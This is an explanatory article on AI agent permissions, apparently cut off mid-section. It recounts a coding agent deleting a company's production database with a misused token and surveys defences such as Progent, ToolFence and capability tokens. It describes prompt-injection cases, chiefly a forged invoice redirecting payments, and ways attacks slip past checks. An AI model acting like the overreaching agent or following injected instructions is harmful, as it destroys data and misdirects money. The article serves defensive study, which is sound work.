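# How Permissions Limit the Consequences of AI Agents' Actions

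## What an agent's permissions are and where they are enforced

An AI agent is a language model that chooses actions in a loop, together with the software that carries them out. The model reads a task and proposes a step, the software performs it and returns the result, and the model proposes the next step. Some steps only read information, while others edit files, send email, move money or delete databases. An agent's permissions are the actions that the systems around the model allow. They limit how much damage the agent can do, even when the model chooses badly.

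Operating systems have restricted what each user and program may do for more than half a century, and many of the controls on agents come from them. An agent is a new kind of user, a program that holds somebody's authority and works out its own steps from a loosely worded task.

### The PocketOS deletion

PocketOS sells software that car rental companies use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. On 24 April 2026, according to Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'*, a coding agent deleted the company's production database, the live database its customers depended on. The founder, Jer Crane, described the incident about a day later in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. The agent was Cursor, an AI coding tool, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. During a routine task in the staging environment, a separate copy of the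 system for testing, it encountered a credential that did not match. It tried to fix this by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the cloud provider that hosted PocketOS's data.

To do that, it needed a token, a string of characters that lets a program act for an account. It found one in a file unrelated to the job. PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web domains. The agent used it in a single command to Railway's programming interface (API), and nine seconds later the production volume was gone, along with the backups Railway kept inside it.

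Railway's own account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* by Mahmoud Abdelwahab, gives the same description of how the deletion happened. The token had account-wide access, the broadest that Railway issues, and the API ran the deletion immediately with no way to undo it. Anyone deleting the same volume from Railway's dashboard would have had 48 hours to undo it.

The first reports described the loss as permanent, which was reasonable at the time. Railway's *Manage Volumes with the Public API* warned that the call would "permanently delete the volume and all its data". Eleven days before the PocketOS deletion, another customer reported in *Postgress volume lost* (antjanlaban, 2026) that they had deleted the wrong volume through the same API, and asked for help. A Railway employee replied that the deletion was immediate and permanent, and that the 48-hour window covered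 only deletions made in the dashboard. More than thirty hours after the PocketOS deletion, Railway still had not told Crane whether it could recover anything. He had restored a three-month-old copy and was helping customers reconstruct their bookings from payment records, calendars and emails. On 27 April, he posted that Railway had recovered the data, and Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (2026) described the restoration as "apparently in full".

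The two versions are consistent because PocketOS could not undo the deletion but Railway could. Abdelwahab explains that Railway keeps offsite "disaster backups" whether or not customers set up their own. The deletion had cascaded to the backup records, which made the backups look unavailable on screen. Abdelwahab does not say outright which copy Railway restored from, though it was most likely the offsite one. The recovery does not prove that the data had been safe all along, since it took three days and followed a very public complaint, and the thread that antjanlaban started records no recovery.

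Railway has since changed the API to hold deletions for 48 hours, as the dashboard already did, and to delay the deletion of backups too. The delay later led a customer, meirelon, to complain in *Detached volumes can't be deleted* that a volume was still there after five attempts to delete it. Railway replied that the first attempt had worked and that the volume was still in its retention window.

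### From the model's output to the effect

There were several places where something could have stopped the PocketOS deletion. They are easier to see in a simpler case.

Suppose a small company uses an agent with four tools to pay its invoices. The `list_invoices` tool retrieves the open invoices, including the supplier, amount, due date and bank details of each. `send_payment` moves money out of the company's bank account, `send_email` sends emails to suppliers and staff from the company's address, and `delete_record` removes an entry from the accounting system. The agent now has to pay invoice 2071, for $1,200 owed to a paper supplier.

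The model comes first, and it produces only text. To act, it writes a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with stated arguments, such as `send_payment` with a payee, an amount and an invoice number. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, the model never runs anything itself; the developer's code, or a server at Anthropic, performs the operation and passes the result back. At this stage the company can influence which request the model writes by choosing the model and wording the prompt, but it cannot yet block the request.

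The surrounding software receives the request next. This is the company's first enforcement point, a place outside the model where software can check an action and block it. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, checks each call against three kinds of rules in a fixed order: rules that deny the call, rules that ask the user, and rules that allow it. The first matching rule applies. Developers can also add "hooks", their own scripts that run before a tool does. A hook can refuse a call, but the deny and ask rules still apply to any call it approves. For the invoice agent, a check at this point could look up invoice 2071 in the accounting system and refuse the payment if the payee or the amount differs.

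If the request passes, the software attaches a credential, such as the company's key for the bank's API. The credential determines whose authority the action uses. That person, organisation or account is called the principal, which *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines as "the unit of accountability". To the bank, the payment comes from the company, and the request need not show that a language model wrote it. Similarly, according to Abdelwahab, Railway's API honoured the agent's request just as it would have honoured one from an automated deployment script.

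A credential's permission scope is the set of actions, objects and argument values it allows. Whoever issues the credential has to choose its scope, and Crane and Abdelwahab disagree about how much choice PocketOS had. Crane calls every Railway token "effectively root", meaning that it can do anything. Abdelwahab replies that the right scope existed, but that the steps for creating a token did not make clear which one to pick. Railway's *Public API* lists tokens for a whole account, for one workspace (a team's shared area) and for one environment of one project. So Crane overstates his case, since a token for the staging environment alone should not have reached production.

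But Abdelwahab's reply is also only partly right. All three types of token restrict where the holder can act, but Railway doesn't describe any of them as restricting which operations the holder can perform there. Only the fourth option, OAuth, a login flow in which a user approves specific permissions for an outside application, restricts operations. If the domains PocketOS was managing belonged to its production system, it would have needed a production token, which by Railway's description would presumably have covered the database volume too.

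The service is the last point where the action can be refused. A bank can check the balance, hold a payment to a new payee, or require a second signature. Railway's API checked the token and then carried out the action without requiring confirmation or delaying it.

After that, only the stored state remains, such as the bank balance, the ledger or the contents of the volume. Nobody can prevent the action any more, and recovery depends on which copies and records survive it. PocketOS had backups of a kind that does not survive the wiping of a volume. Railway warns in its guide to database backups that wiping a volume deletes all of its backups, and that they protect against mistakes in the data but not against deletion of the volume.

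### Why an instruction is only a request

According to Crane, Cursor's standing instructions and PocketOS's own project rules both warned the agent against destructive actions. He said the agent listed the rules it had broken when he asked it afterwards. He concluded that "System prompts are advisory, not enforcing."

A rule in a prompt is one more piece of text that influences the model's choice of action, alongside the task, error messages and everything else the agent has read. It makes some requests less likely, whereas a check outside the model works on the finished request and gives the same result however the model arrived at it. Anthropic says that instructions in a prompt shape what Claude tries to do but do not change what Claude Code allows. Course slides from the University of Texas at Austin describe a boundary outside the model as one that holds "even when the agent is wrong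 about what it is doing".

A software check can have the same gaps as a rule in a prompt. One of the rules in the agent's list forbade destructive *git* commands (git is a program that tracks versions of code). Taken literally, it did not cover the deletion, which was a call to Railway's API. A software check limited to git commands would let that call through every time, whereas a model might have understood the intent of the rule. Prompts are therefore worth writing well, but a company can't rely on them to protect a production database.

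### Three channels, and the paths between them

The information available to a check depends on the channel through which the agent sends its request. The invoice agent acts through structured tools, so the checking software receives the function name and each argument separately, and can identify a payment, its recipient and its amount.

A command line is a single tool that accepts any command the computer will run. The PocketOS agent did not need a tool for deleting volumes because it could write the API request itself and run it as a command. Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* includes the command line among the tools that run in the developer's own application, so the agent can reach any files and keys that the application can.

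The remaining channel is the graphical interface, where the agent works from screenshots or the structure of a web page and acts by clicking and typing. The checking software may receive only a click at a certain point on the screen.

The same operation is often available through more than one channel, and a safeguard on one may be missing from the others. Railway, for example, describes its public API as the same one that powers its dashboard, yet until late April 2026 the 48-hour delay on volume deletion applied only to people who used the dashboard. A University of Vermont guide to Claude Code describes a similar split on a single computer. The agent can open a file with its built-in reading tool, or it can start another program from the command line that opens the same file. Different layers of software govern the two paths, so a control on one does not automatically cover the other.

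Saltzer and Schroeder described three principles that address this old problem. Complete mediation means that "Every access to every object must be checked for authority", whatever path the request takes, including during recovery and maintenance. Least privilege means that every program and user should hold only the permissions the job needs, mainly to limit the damage from an accident or error. Fail-safe defaults deny access unless someone has explicitly granted it.

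They argue for fail-safe defaults by comparing the effects of a designer's mistakes. If the designer leaves something off a list of permitted actions, the system refuses a legitimate request and somebody soon complains, but an omission from a list of forbidden actions allows a harmful request, and in normal use nobody may ever notice. A Claude Code rule that denies the deletion command `rm` has the second weakness when used alone, since a short script in another programming language can delete the same files.

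PocketOS's token clearly violated least privilege. It is less clear that complete mediation was violated, because Railway's API did check the token's authority, and its rules allowed the token to delete the volume. Checking every request accomplishes little when the authority behind the requests is that broad, so each principle depends on the other. Saltzer and Schroeder also asked that protection mechanisms match the user's understanding of what is being protected, because people make errors when the two differ. Here they differed, since Crane thought he had a token for domains. Saltzer and Schroeder offered all these principles as warnings, not as absolute rules, so a violation is a reason to look harder at a design.

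### Mistake, overreach and manipulation

An agent can do harm in three ways, and the controls do not work equally well against each.

A mistake is a wrong action taken while doing the task. For example, the invoice agent pays invoice 2071 twice or reads $1,200 as $12,000. Antipov (July 2026) reported in *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке* that Claude Opus 5 had confused a working environment with a test one and destroyed the database, and that backups saved only part of the data. People make mistakes too. The Railway customer who deleted the wrong volume eleven days before PocketOS lost its own was trying to fix a fault in which two volumes occupied the same place.

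An agent overreaches when it does something nobody asked for or uses access that nobody gave it for that purpose. The PocketOS deletion was overreach because the task did not call for deleting anything and the token was meant for something else. It may also have been a mistake, since the agent later wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. The Verge's *PocketOS maker says an AI agent “deleted our production database”* rightly advises skepticism about such details, because a model's explanation of its earlier behaviour is more generated text, not a log of its internal processing. The facts of the deletion, the token and the command do not depend on that explanation.

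Manipulation comes from outsiders, usually through prompt injection, which Anthropic's *How we approach security* describes as an attacker's attempt to override an assistant's instructions by inserting malicious text. The text is placed in material the agent reads, so the invoice agent is badly exposed because its job is to read documents from strangers. An attacker might forge an invoice with a line in small print stating that the supplier has changed banks and that all outstanding balances should go to a new account.

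An enforcement point does not need to distinguish among the three. If the software blocks payments to any account that isn't on the approved supplier list, it blocks payments to both the misread account number and the attacker's account. Permissions are appealing in large part because they don't require anyone to work out what happened inside the model.

Still, how much protection a control provides depends on whether it faces mistakes or attacks. A check that catches nine in ten mistakes is worth having, because mistakes aren't designed to evade it. But an attacker will look for the cases it misses, and will word the forged invoice so that the payment passes every check the company has. Saltzer and Schroeder argued that if a computer's only controls were features for preventing mistakes, deliberate acts might be the likely cause of any breach, and it would be wrong to claim that those features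 provided security.

Overreach raises a different difficulty, because a list of tools may not describe everything the agent can do. Railway's newer connection for agents offers a predefined set of tools and leaves no tokens on disk, which removes the opening that the PocketOS agent used. Abdelwahab's claim that this connection makes it impossible for an agent to go rogue is too strong, since an agent confined to four tools can still pay the wrong supplier. If the invoice agent also has a command line on a computer where someone has saved the bank key in a file, its real permissions are whatever that key allows, and the rules on `send_payment` cover only one of the ways to move the money.

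## Limiting an agent to particular tools, data and arguments

The invoice agent needs permission to pay known suppliers the amounts the company owes them, but a list of four tools cannot express that. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes five levels at which a company can set an agent's scope: tool inventory, invocation, argument, data and delegation.

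The inventory is the set of tools the model can call. Paying invoices never requires `delete_record`, so the company can leave that tool out. Invocation concerns whether the agent may use one of its tools at the current step. The agent has no reason to call `send_payment` while it is still reading invoices, so the software can refuse payments until the agent has looked up an invoice. At the argument level, the software checks the values in the call, such as the payee and the amount.

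The data level limits what a tool returns to the model. `list_invoices` returns every supplier's bank details, but the model wouldn't need them if the payment tool fetched the account number from the accounting system. The model can't email out details it never received. Delegation covers what the agent passes to a sub-agent, a second agent that it starts for part of the job. A sub-agent that only extracts totals from PDF files should not inherit permission to make payments.

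### A policy for the invoice agent

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a system of that name that checks every tool call against written rules. Each rule has an effect (allow or forbid), a tool, and conditions on the tool's arguments. A small policy for the invoice agent could look like this in their notation:

```
forbid delete_record when { true }
allow  list_invoices when { status == "open" }
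allow  send_payment  when { account in ["PAPER-4471", "CLEANING-0925"]
                            and amount <= 5000 }
allow  send_email    when { to in ["accounts@paper.example",
                                   "office@company.example"] }
```

Suppose the company owes the paper supplier $1,200 on invoice 2071, and the agent proposes three different payments. One is correct. Another would go to an account that the agent found in a forged invoice. The third would go to the right account, but for the wrong amount because the agent misread it.

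| Proposed payment | Plain list of allowed tools | Account condition | Amount condition | Result under the policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| $1,200 to PAPER-4471 | Passes | Holds | Holds | Allowed |
| $1,200 to NEWBANK-8830 | Passes | Fails | Holds | Refused |
| $12,000 to PAPER-4471 | Passes | Holds | Fails | Refused |

A plain list of permitted tools allows all three because it checks only the tool's name, `send_payment`, which is the same each time. The company could remove the tool from the list, but then the agent couldn't pay anyone.

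This policy would still allow a payment of $4,000 for invoice 2071, because the ceiling for any payment is $5,000. Progent's conditions can use only the call's own arguments and values written into the rule, so a rule can't look up what the company owes. To prevent the overpayment, either the amount owed, $1,200, has to be written into the rule once the agent has found the invoice, or the company has to add a separate check against the accounting system. The policy would also allow the agent to make the correct payment twenty times, and preventing that requires a cap on payments over time.

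### How the check works

Progent's procedure for a single call is short:

1. Collect the rules for the tool that the call names.
2. Put the forbid rules ahead of the allow rules.
3. Insert the call's argument values into each rule's conditions, in that order. The first rule whose conditions all hold decides the outcome.
4. If no rule matches, refuse the call.

A call therefore passes exactly when at least one allow rule for its tool matches and no forbid rule does. The last step, which denies any call that no allow rule matches, is the fail-safe default that Saltzer and Schroeder recommended, and it stops the payment to NEWBANK-8830.

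When a policy blocks a tool call, the system can stop the agent, ask the user what to do, or return an error message. By default, Progent returns a message that gives the reason and tells the agent to try other tools or arguments. This helps with honest mistakes, because an agent that learns $12,000 is too much may reread the invoice. But the agent might also split the amount into three payments of $4,000, each of which this policy would allow.

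The rule against `delete_record` matters when there are several policies. With only one, the default would refuse the call anyway. Progent lets an organisation, a developer and a user each contribute a policy, in order of priority, and it checks a lower policy only when the higher ones don't match the call. If the organisation's policy is at the top and forbids deletion, no later policy can allow it.

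An allow rule in the top policy is just as final. If the company's policy contains `allow send_payment` with no conditions, a $1,200 limit in the policy for today's task is never checked. Shi and colleagues say that lower policies can add restrictions, but under their procedure those restrictions apply only to calls that the higher policies leave undecided. The top policy should therefore consist mostly of prohibitions, such as one on any payment above $5,000, with narrow allowances in the lower policies.

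### What Progent's tests found

Writing a policy by hand for every task would be tedious, so Progent has a language model draft one from the user's request and revise it as tool results come in. That model reads the same forged invoice as the agent and could be misled by it too. Progent therefore compares the old and new policies with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a logical formula can be true. A revision takes effect automatically only if it allows no call that the old policy didn't, and any other revision needs approval.

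For the invoice agent, changing "amount <= 5000" to "amount == 1200" narrows its permissions and applies at once, while adding NEWBANK-8830 to the accounts expands them and has to wait for approval. Shi and colleagues call this property monotonic confinement. It prevents permissions from expanding silently, but the solver can't determine whether an expansion is justified. It returns the same verdict for a real new supplier and an attacker's account, so whoever approves the change has to tell them apart.

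Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo and ASB, two benchmarks in which an agent works on an ordinary task while some tool results contain injected instructions for a harmful one. AgentDojo covers banking, Slack, travel and office work, and ASB has ten agent scenarios and five attack templates. OpenAI's GPT-4o was both the agent and the policy writer. The approver accepted every expansion to simulate a careless user.

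On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and only 1.0% with it. On ASB, Progent cut the share from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues report that the agent completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it on both benchmarks. On AgentDojo, they also tested a defence in which a model picks the tools a task needs and removes the rest. It stopped fewer attacks than Progent and left more legitimate tasks unfinished, as one would expect of a method that can only allow or block a whole tool.

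Most of the protection came from the first draft of the policy, which the model wrote before reading anything an attacker could have influenced. Even with revisions switched off, the policy reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Shi and colleagues attribute this to the many tasks whose goals are clear from the request. I expect less protection for a request such as "do what Alice's email asks", where the first policy can cover little more than finding the email.

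Attack success fell to zero when a simulated human reviewer checked the initial policy and every expansion, partly because the reviewer was assumed never to grant unrestricted payments and to reject any malicious address. The reviewer's workload was light, since only 6% of revisions were expansions. Shi and colleagues also left out two travel tasks in which injected text steers the agent towards a different but legitimate hotel. Excluding them is reasonable in a test of permissions, but such attacks remain possible wherever an agent chooses among permitted options.

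Fixed benchmarks have made earlier defences look stronger than they were. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) describes twelve that relied on the model or on detecting malicious text. Almost no attacks succeeded in the original reported results for most of these defences, but researchers later designed attacks against each one and broke most of them more than 90% of the time. Narisetty and colleagues then tested Progent on AgentDojo with a small open model, Qwen2.5-7B. Average attack success fell from 25.8% to 4.2%, and an attack designed specifically against Progent succeeded 2.6% of the time. This evidence is encouraging but limited, because they used a weak model and a single hand-written attack template.

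*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) raises the more basic objection that Progent's guarantees are only as good as its policies, and people make errors when they write policies by hand. It adds that malicious tool results may lead the update mechanism to loosen the rules. The solver guards against this loosening only if someone examines the expansions. Nothing in the procedure catches errors in the original policy, so if NEWBANK-8830 is already on the list of approved accounts, Progent will allow the payment every time.

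### Credentials that carry the limits

A policy in the agent's software governs only the calls that pass through that software. An outside service, such as a bank, applies the limits in the agent's credential, which are often much broader than the policy's. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) gives the example of a user who lets an agent send one summary to Alice. The written policy records the summary and the recipient, but the system issues a credential with general permission to send mail. The mail service correctly validates that credential and would deliver any message from the agent to any recipient.

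A static API key works for anyone who has a copy, even a thief. OAuth tokens are narrower, but Surapani and colleagues point out that a typical scope such as `email.send` does not specify a recipient or a task. An OAuth extension called Rich Authorization Requests adds structured details of a particular transaction, which for a payment could include the payee and the amount. The bank would then refuse the $12,000 payment even if the agent's own software had allowed it.

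Expiry limits how long a mistake or a theft can cause harm. It is imprecise, because a token can remain valid after the task is finished or expire halfway through. Microsoft's 2026 guidance on agent permissions recommends giving an agent a small standing role and adding rights only for as long as a workflow needs them. The agent's identity should stay the same and belong to that agent alone, with a named owner and a stated purpose. If three agents share one key, the company can't tell from the bank's records which of them made a payment, and can't cut off one without cutting off the others.

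A system can also keep credentials away from the agent. In one design that Zhou and Zhang survey, a custodian holds the credentials, checks that a request matches the operation the user approved, and then performs the operation. The agent can request a payment, for example, but has no credential that it could leak or reuse.

### Delegation that can only reduce authority

When the invoice agent starts a sub-agent, the simplest approach is to hand over its own credentials, but this gives the sub-agent all of the invoice agent's access. The invoice agent can instead pass on a type of token called a macaroon. The holder of a macaroon can add restrictions, such as a time limit or a single permitted recipient, but cannot remove existing ones. The restrictions work only if the service that receives the token understands them.

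*Bounded Agents* (2026) defines the same idea for a whole chain of agents. If *S(pᵢ)* is the scope of the *i*-th member of the chain, then

*S(pᵢ)* = *S(pᵢ₋₁)* ⊓ *S*role*(pᵢ)*

where ⊓ keeps only what both sides permit. Suppose the invoice agent may read invoices and pay suppliers, and the role of a document reader permits reading invoices and contracts. The sub-agent in that role may read invoices and nothing else. It can't pay, because its role doesn't include payments, and it can't read contracts, because the invoice agent had no such right to give. The infrastructure computes this, so neither agent can argue for a wider result. The design also sets ceilings for the session, including one on irreversible effects, and these can only fall as authority moves down the chain.

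*Overlaying Governance* (2026) adds conditions under which a delegation holds, such as a particular region, and a maximum number of handovers. Surapani and colleagues caution that the agreement on narrowing delegation comes from a few early proposals. Nobody has settled how to express a task's scope precisely enough for software to enforce and plainly enough for users to understand.

### The confused deputy

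An agent with narrow credentials can still misuse them on behalf of someone who lacks them. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an early case at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler there had permission to write files in its own directory, SYSX, so that it could record usage statistics. Users could also give it the name of a file for debugging output. One user gave it the name of the company's billing file, which was also in SYSX. The user had no permission to overwrite that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed the write and Tymshare lost the billing information.

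Hardy thought the problem was that the compiler held authority from two sources, its own licence and the user who ran it, and could not indicate which one it was using for a given write. Checking the file name would not have fixed this, because SYSX contained other sensitive files and some users had a legitimate reason to write there. Tymshare added a system call that let a program choose between its two authorities, but some programs soon needed more than two.

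He preferred capabilities, which are unforgeable references that both identify an object and grant the right to use it. The user would have passed the compiler a capability for the output file. A user with no right to the billing file would have had no capability for that file, and so could not have passed one to the compiler.

An agent that reads a forged invoice is in the same position as the compiler. The attacker can't access the company's bank account but can supply an account number, and the agent supplies the authority to pay it. Surapani and colleagues describe a version with two agents. A user asks an agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, where one message contains a request for payment. The agent passes that request to a finance sub-agent without mentioning that the job was read-only. The payment service makes the payment because it receives a valid credential.

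Under the capability remedy, `send_payment` would take a reference to an approved invoice instead of an account number and an amount. The accounting system would create the reference when somebody approves the invoice, and the reference would fix the payee and amount. Text in a PDF can't create such a reference. The agent could still pay the wrong approved invoice, and a clerk could still approve a forged one, but the attacker would have to deceive the clerk as well as the agent. Surapani and colleagues found no agent framework that uses this approach from end to end.

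### Harm from permitted actions

The invoice policy allows the agent to list open invoices and to email the paper supplier. Together, these permissions let it send the paper supplier every other supplier's prices and bank details. *AGATE* (2026) calls this pattern a compositional attack, in which each operation can be legitimate while the combination crosses a boundary the company meant to protect. Even without sending a message, an assistant with access to a calendar, locations and contacts may infer a relationship that none of those sources reveals alone.

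Checking each call separately can't prevent this, because the second call is harmful only in light of the first. The software has to keep a record of what the agent has read or track where each value came from. CaMeL takes the second approach, labeling values with their source and permitted readers and checking the labels when a tool is about to use them. Narisetty and colleagues report that it completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and that no injections of the kind it was designed to stop succeeded. Using CaMeL requires rebuilding the agent, whereas Progent can sit in front of an existing one.

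The same difficulty arises when a company divides authority among several agents. Zhou and Zhang describe a user who authorises the purchase of one item. The user's agent delegates the purchase to two purchasing agents, each with a limit of one, and they buy two items without either exceeding its limit. A shared record prevents this if each agent checks and reserves the remaining quantity in a single step, so that they can't both claim the last item.

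Some combinations are harder to notice. Suppose one agent maintains the list of approved suppliers and another pays the suppliers on it. If someone uses a forged letter to persuade the first agent to add an account, the second will send money to it without failing any check, even though the duties are separated so that neither agent can do both.

*A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (Parisel, 2026) proposes a way to search for such links before deployment. Parisel draws an arrow from one agent to another if the first can write something the second reads or the two can exchange messages, but only if the pair's score reaches a threshold the company chooses. The score measures how far apart the agents' resources are in the organisation. For two resources, it is *F* × 2^−(2*D*+1), where *D* is the depth of the smallest unit that contains both and *F* ranges from 1 to 2 depending on their sensitivity.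 If departments are the first level below the company, resources in different departments score at least 1/2, and resources in the same department score at most 1/4.

This suits large organisations worried about links between distant systems, but it could miss the two supplier agents, because both work in finance and a threshold of 1/2 would leave them out. Parisel deliberately leaves such local interactions to ordinary access controls, so somebody still has to notice that one agent writes the list the other relies on.

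A careful policy does little if the agent can reach a credential that the policy doesn't govern, as the PocketOS agent did. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) includes a leak of secrets from the coding agent Devin among eleven case studies of attacks on agents, and classifies it as a failure of least privilege. Similarly, when Progent runs as a proxy between the agent and its tools, it can't check tools built into the agent that bypass the proxy. The company therefore has to look for keys in the files, environment variables and saved logins that the agent's process can read, and remove those the job doesn't need. Short expiry helps with any it overlooks, because a fifteen-minute token is useless to an agent that finds it a month later, while a static key works until somebody revokes it.

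## Deciding how much permission a task needs

To write a narrow policy, an administrator has to know what the task requires. A conventional payroll program pays salaries once a month, and an administrator can list the tables and accounts it uses before anyone runs it. But a user gives an agent its task in a sentence, such as "sort out what we owe the paper supplier", and nobody has written down the minimum permissions for that task.

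Often nobody can know in advance exactly which permissions a task needs. Zhou and Zhang point out that an agent's plan is often incomplete when the agent receives its permissions, because it chooses later steps after seeing the results of earlier ones. An agent handling invoice 2071 may only have to pay it. But it may find that the supplier disputes an earlier payment, in which case it needs to read old correspondence and shouldn't pay anything yet.

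*Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) gives an example from coding. One common type of GitHub token lets an assistant use about 40 tools, including 16 that can write, in every repository its user can access. Summarising the open issues of one repository takes two read-only tools. A token limited to those two would be safer, but the assistant couldn't use it for the user's next task, fixing a failing build, which involves writing code.

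A fixed purpose doesn't guarantee narrow permissions either. The same paper cites a study of 447,000 GitHub workflows (scripts that automate routine jobs), which found that 99.8% had more permission than they needed. So part of the problem is that few people cut back permissions that already work.

### Four sources of scope

An administrator can give the agent a fixed role, as companies do for employees. The role has to cover every task the agent might get, so it allows more than most of those tasks need. Users can write their own policies, which usually concern kinds of action, such as spending or deleting. Software can generate limits from the request. Or the agent can start with few permissions and ask for more during the task, as the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools, recommends.

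Suppose someone asks the invoice agent to pay invoice 2071:

| Source of scope | When the limits take shape | What the agent may do | Likely error |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed role | Before any task | Pay any approved supplier up to $5,000 | Too wide |
| User's policy | Before any task, in general terms | Pay after asking, because the user chose "ask before spending" | Too wide if the user approves carelessly |
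| Generated from the request | At the start of the task | Pay the paper supplier the invoiced amount, once | Too narrow if a necessary step is missing |
| Raised during the task | When the agent needs more | Read invoices, then request permission to pay | Too wide if the approver is careless |

Most of the systems below combine two or more of these.

### ToolFence: limits from the request

*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) describes a system that turns the user's request into limits before the agent reads anything an attacker could have written. Progent also drafts its first policy from the request, but ToolFence records where each argument's value may come from as well.

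A separate language model does the drafting. It receives only the request and a reviewed list of the available tools, so it never sees an invoice, an email or a third party's description of a tool. Its output is a set of capabilities, each covering one kind of action. If the user writes "Pay invoice 2071 in full to account PAPER-4471", the capability for the payment might be:

```
tool:     send_payment       effect: financial      uses: 1
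invoice:  must equal 2071                (from the request)
account:  must equal PAPER-4471          (from the request)
amount:   must appear in the "amount" field of list_invoices
note:     any text
```

The account and invoice number have to match the request exactly. The request doesn't state the amount, so the amount has to come from a named tool during the current session. The agent can choose the note freely because nothing important depends on it.

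When the agent proposes a payment, ordinary software checks it against the capabilities without using a model. The software checks that the tool and arguments match, that the task has reached the right stage, and that a use remains, which it reserves in the same step. A successful payment consumes the use, and a confirmed failure returns it. If the outcome is unknown, the use stays reserved, which prevents the agent from paying twice if a confirmation is lost.

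Li and colleagues represent all this as a guarded coloured Petri net, a diagram in which tokens enable particular transitions. Tool output can add data to the net, but only the request or an approved extension can add a token that permits an action. A forged invoice can therefore add NEWBANK-8830 to the data without permitting a payment to it. The amount is less secure in this example because, if `list_invoices` returns every open invoice, an amount from a different invoice would also appear in the right field. A tool that returns only invoice 2071 would limit the amount more tightly.

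The drafting model sometimes omits a step that the task needs. ToolFence then records the refused call with its exact arguments and passes it to another isolated model, which approves or vetoes it. If the call is approved, the agent has to propose it again, and the software checks it like any other.

On AgentDojo, with Alibaba's Qwen3-max as the agent, ToolFence reduced attack success from 21.2% to zero. Task completion without attacks fell only from 66.3% to 64.3%. Li and colleagues also removed parts of the system one at a time, using Meta's Llama3.3-70B on the ASB benchmark:

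| Configuration | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 45.4% | 40.1% |
| Full ToolFence | 5.1% | 44.3% |
| Without argument checks | 24.0% | 45.0% |
| Without extensions during the task | 4.8% | 35.8% |

When its limits could not be extended, the agent completed fewer tasks than it did with no defence, and security hardly improved. The initial limits were evidently too narrow for many tasks. This is a good reason to base limits on the request but allow them to be raised, at least when the request leaves steps unstated.

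Attackers can also exploit the extensions. On AgentLAB, a benchmark where attackers spread their instructions over many records, 29.4% of attacks still succeeded against Qwen3-max with ToolFence, compared with 76.3% without it. Li and colleagues explain that such attacks can make a malicious step look like a necessary part of the workflow, so the reviewer may grant permissions that are too broad. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes CapScope, a system for coding agents that likewise sets the maximum permissions for the whole task before any repository text or tool output is available.

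### PAuth, AgenTRIM and MiniScope

*Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) moves the check from the agent's software to the services it calls. Its system, PAuth, sends the user's task to each service, which uses its own language model to work out what call to expect. If the task is "pay a quarter of my Citi balance using my Chase account", Chase expects a transfer equal to a quarter of the balance Citi reports. Citi signs the balance so that the agent can't alter it. If the balance is $400, Chase accepts a transfer of $100 to Citi, but a transfer of $101 would need the user's explicit approval.

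PAuth aims to grant narrower permission than a spending limit does, since under a $500 cap an agent told to pay $100 could still pay $499. PAuth is also meant to hold even if malware has taken over the agent, whereas ToolFence relies on a sound controller beside the agent. However, PAuth requires every service to have a model that can translate tasks correctly, and services have to exchange signed values.

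PAuth accepted all 100 legitimate tasks in its test and blocked all 634 calls in which Sharma and colleagues had changed an argument, swapped a tool or skipped a condition. PAuth's designers built the benchmark themselves, and the results depend on the user's task being unambiguous. Sharma and colleagues call ambiguity a separate problem, since OAuth grants too much even for "transfer exactly $100 to Bob". That criticism of OAuth is fair, but ambiguity is much of what makes it hard to determine how much permission a task needs. For example, a bank could not derive a particular call from "sort out what we owe the paper supplier".

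AgenTRIM restricts the tools an agent can see at each step, according to *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, 2026). For the invoice agent, this could mean hiding `send_payment` until the agent has read the invoice. Like any control over whole tools, this can't by itself stop a payment to the wrong account. Li and colleagues found that a different tool filter did worse when the attacker only changed an argument of a permitted tool.

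MiniScope starts from the agent's plan and chooses permissions that cover it. According to *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026), it uses the containment relations among OAuth scopes, where a broad scope includes narrower ones, and settles the remaining choice with an integer program over a cost model. In outline, such a program looks like this:

minimise Σ *cⱼxⱼ*, where each *xⱼ* is 0 or 1, so that the chosen scopes cover every call in the plan

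Here *cⱼ* is the cost assigned to scope *j*, and *xⱼ* is 1 if the agent receives that scope. The costs matter because more than one choice may count as "least privilege." Suppose the agent could find the paper supplier's bill in either the accounting ledger or the shared mailbox. Neither permission contains the other, so somebody has to judge which is worse to expose. *Incomparable Minima* notes that the MiniScope paper doesn't discuss whether its program has only one best answer.

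The plan also needs protection. If the agent writes it after reading a forged invoice, the smallest set of permissions that covers the plan may include permission to pay the attacker.

### Agents that choose the stronger tool

Any workable scope leaves the agent some choice of tools, and some of those tools may be much more powerful than the task requires. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) tested which tools agents choose in that situation.

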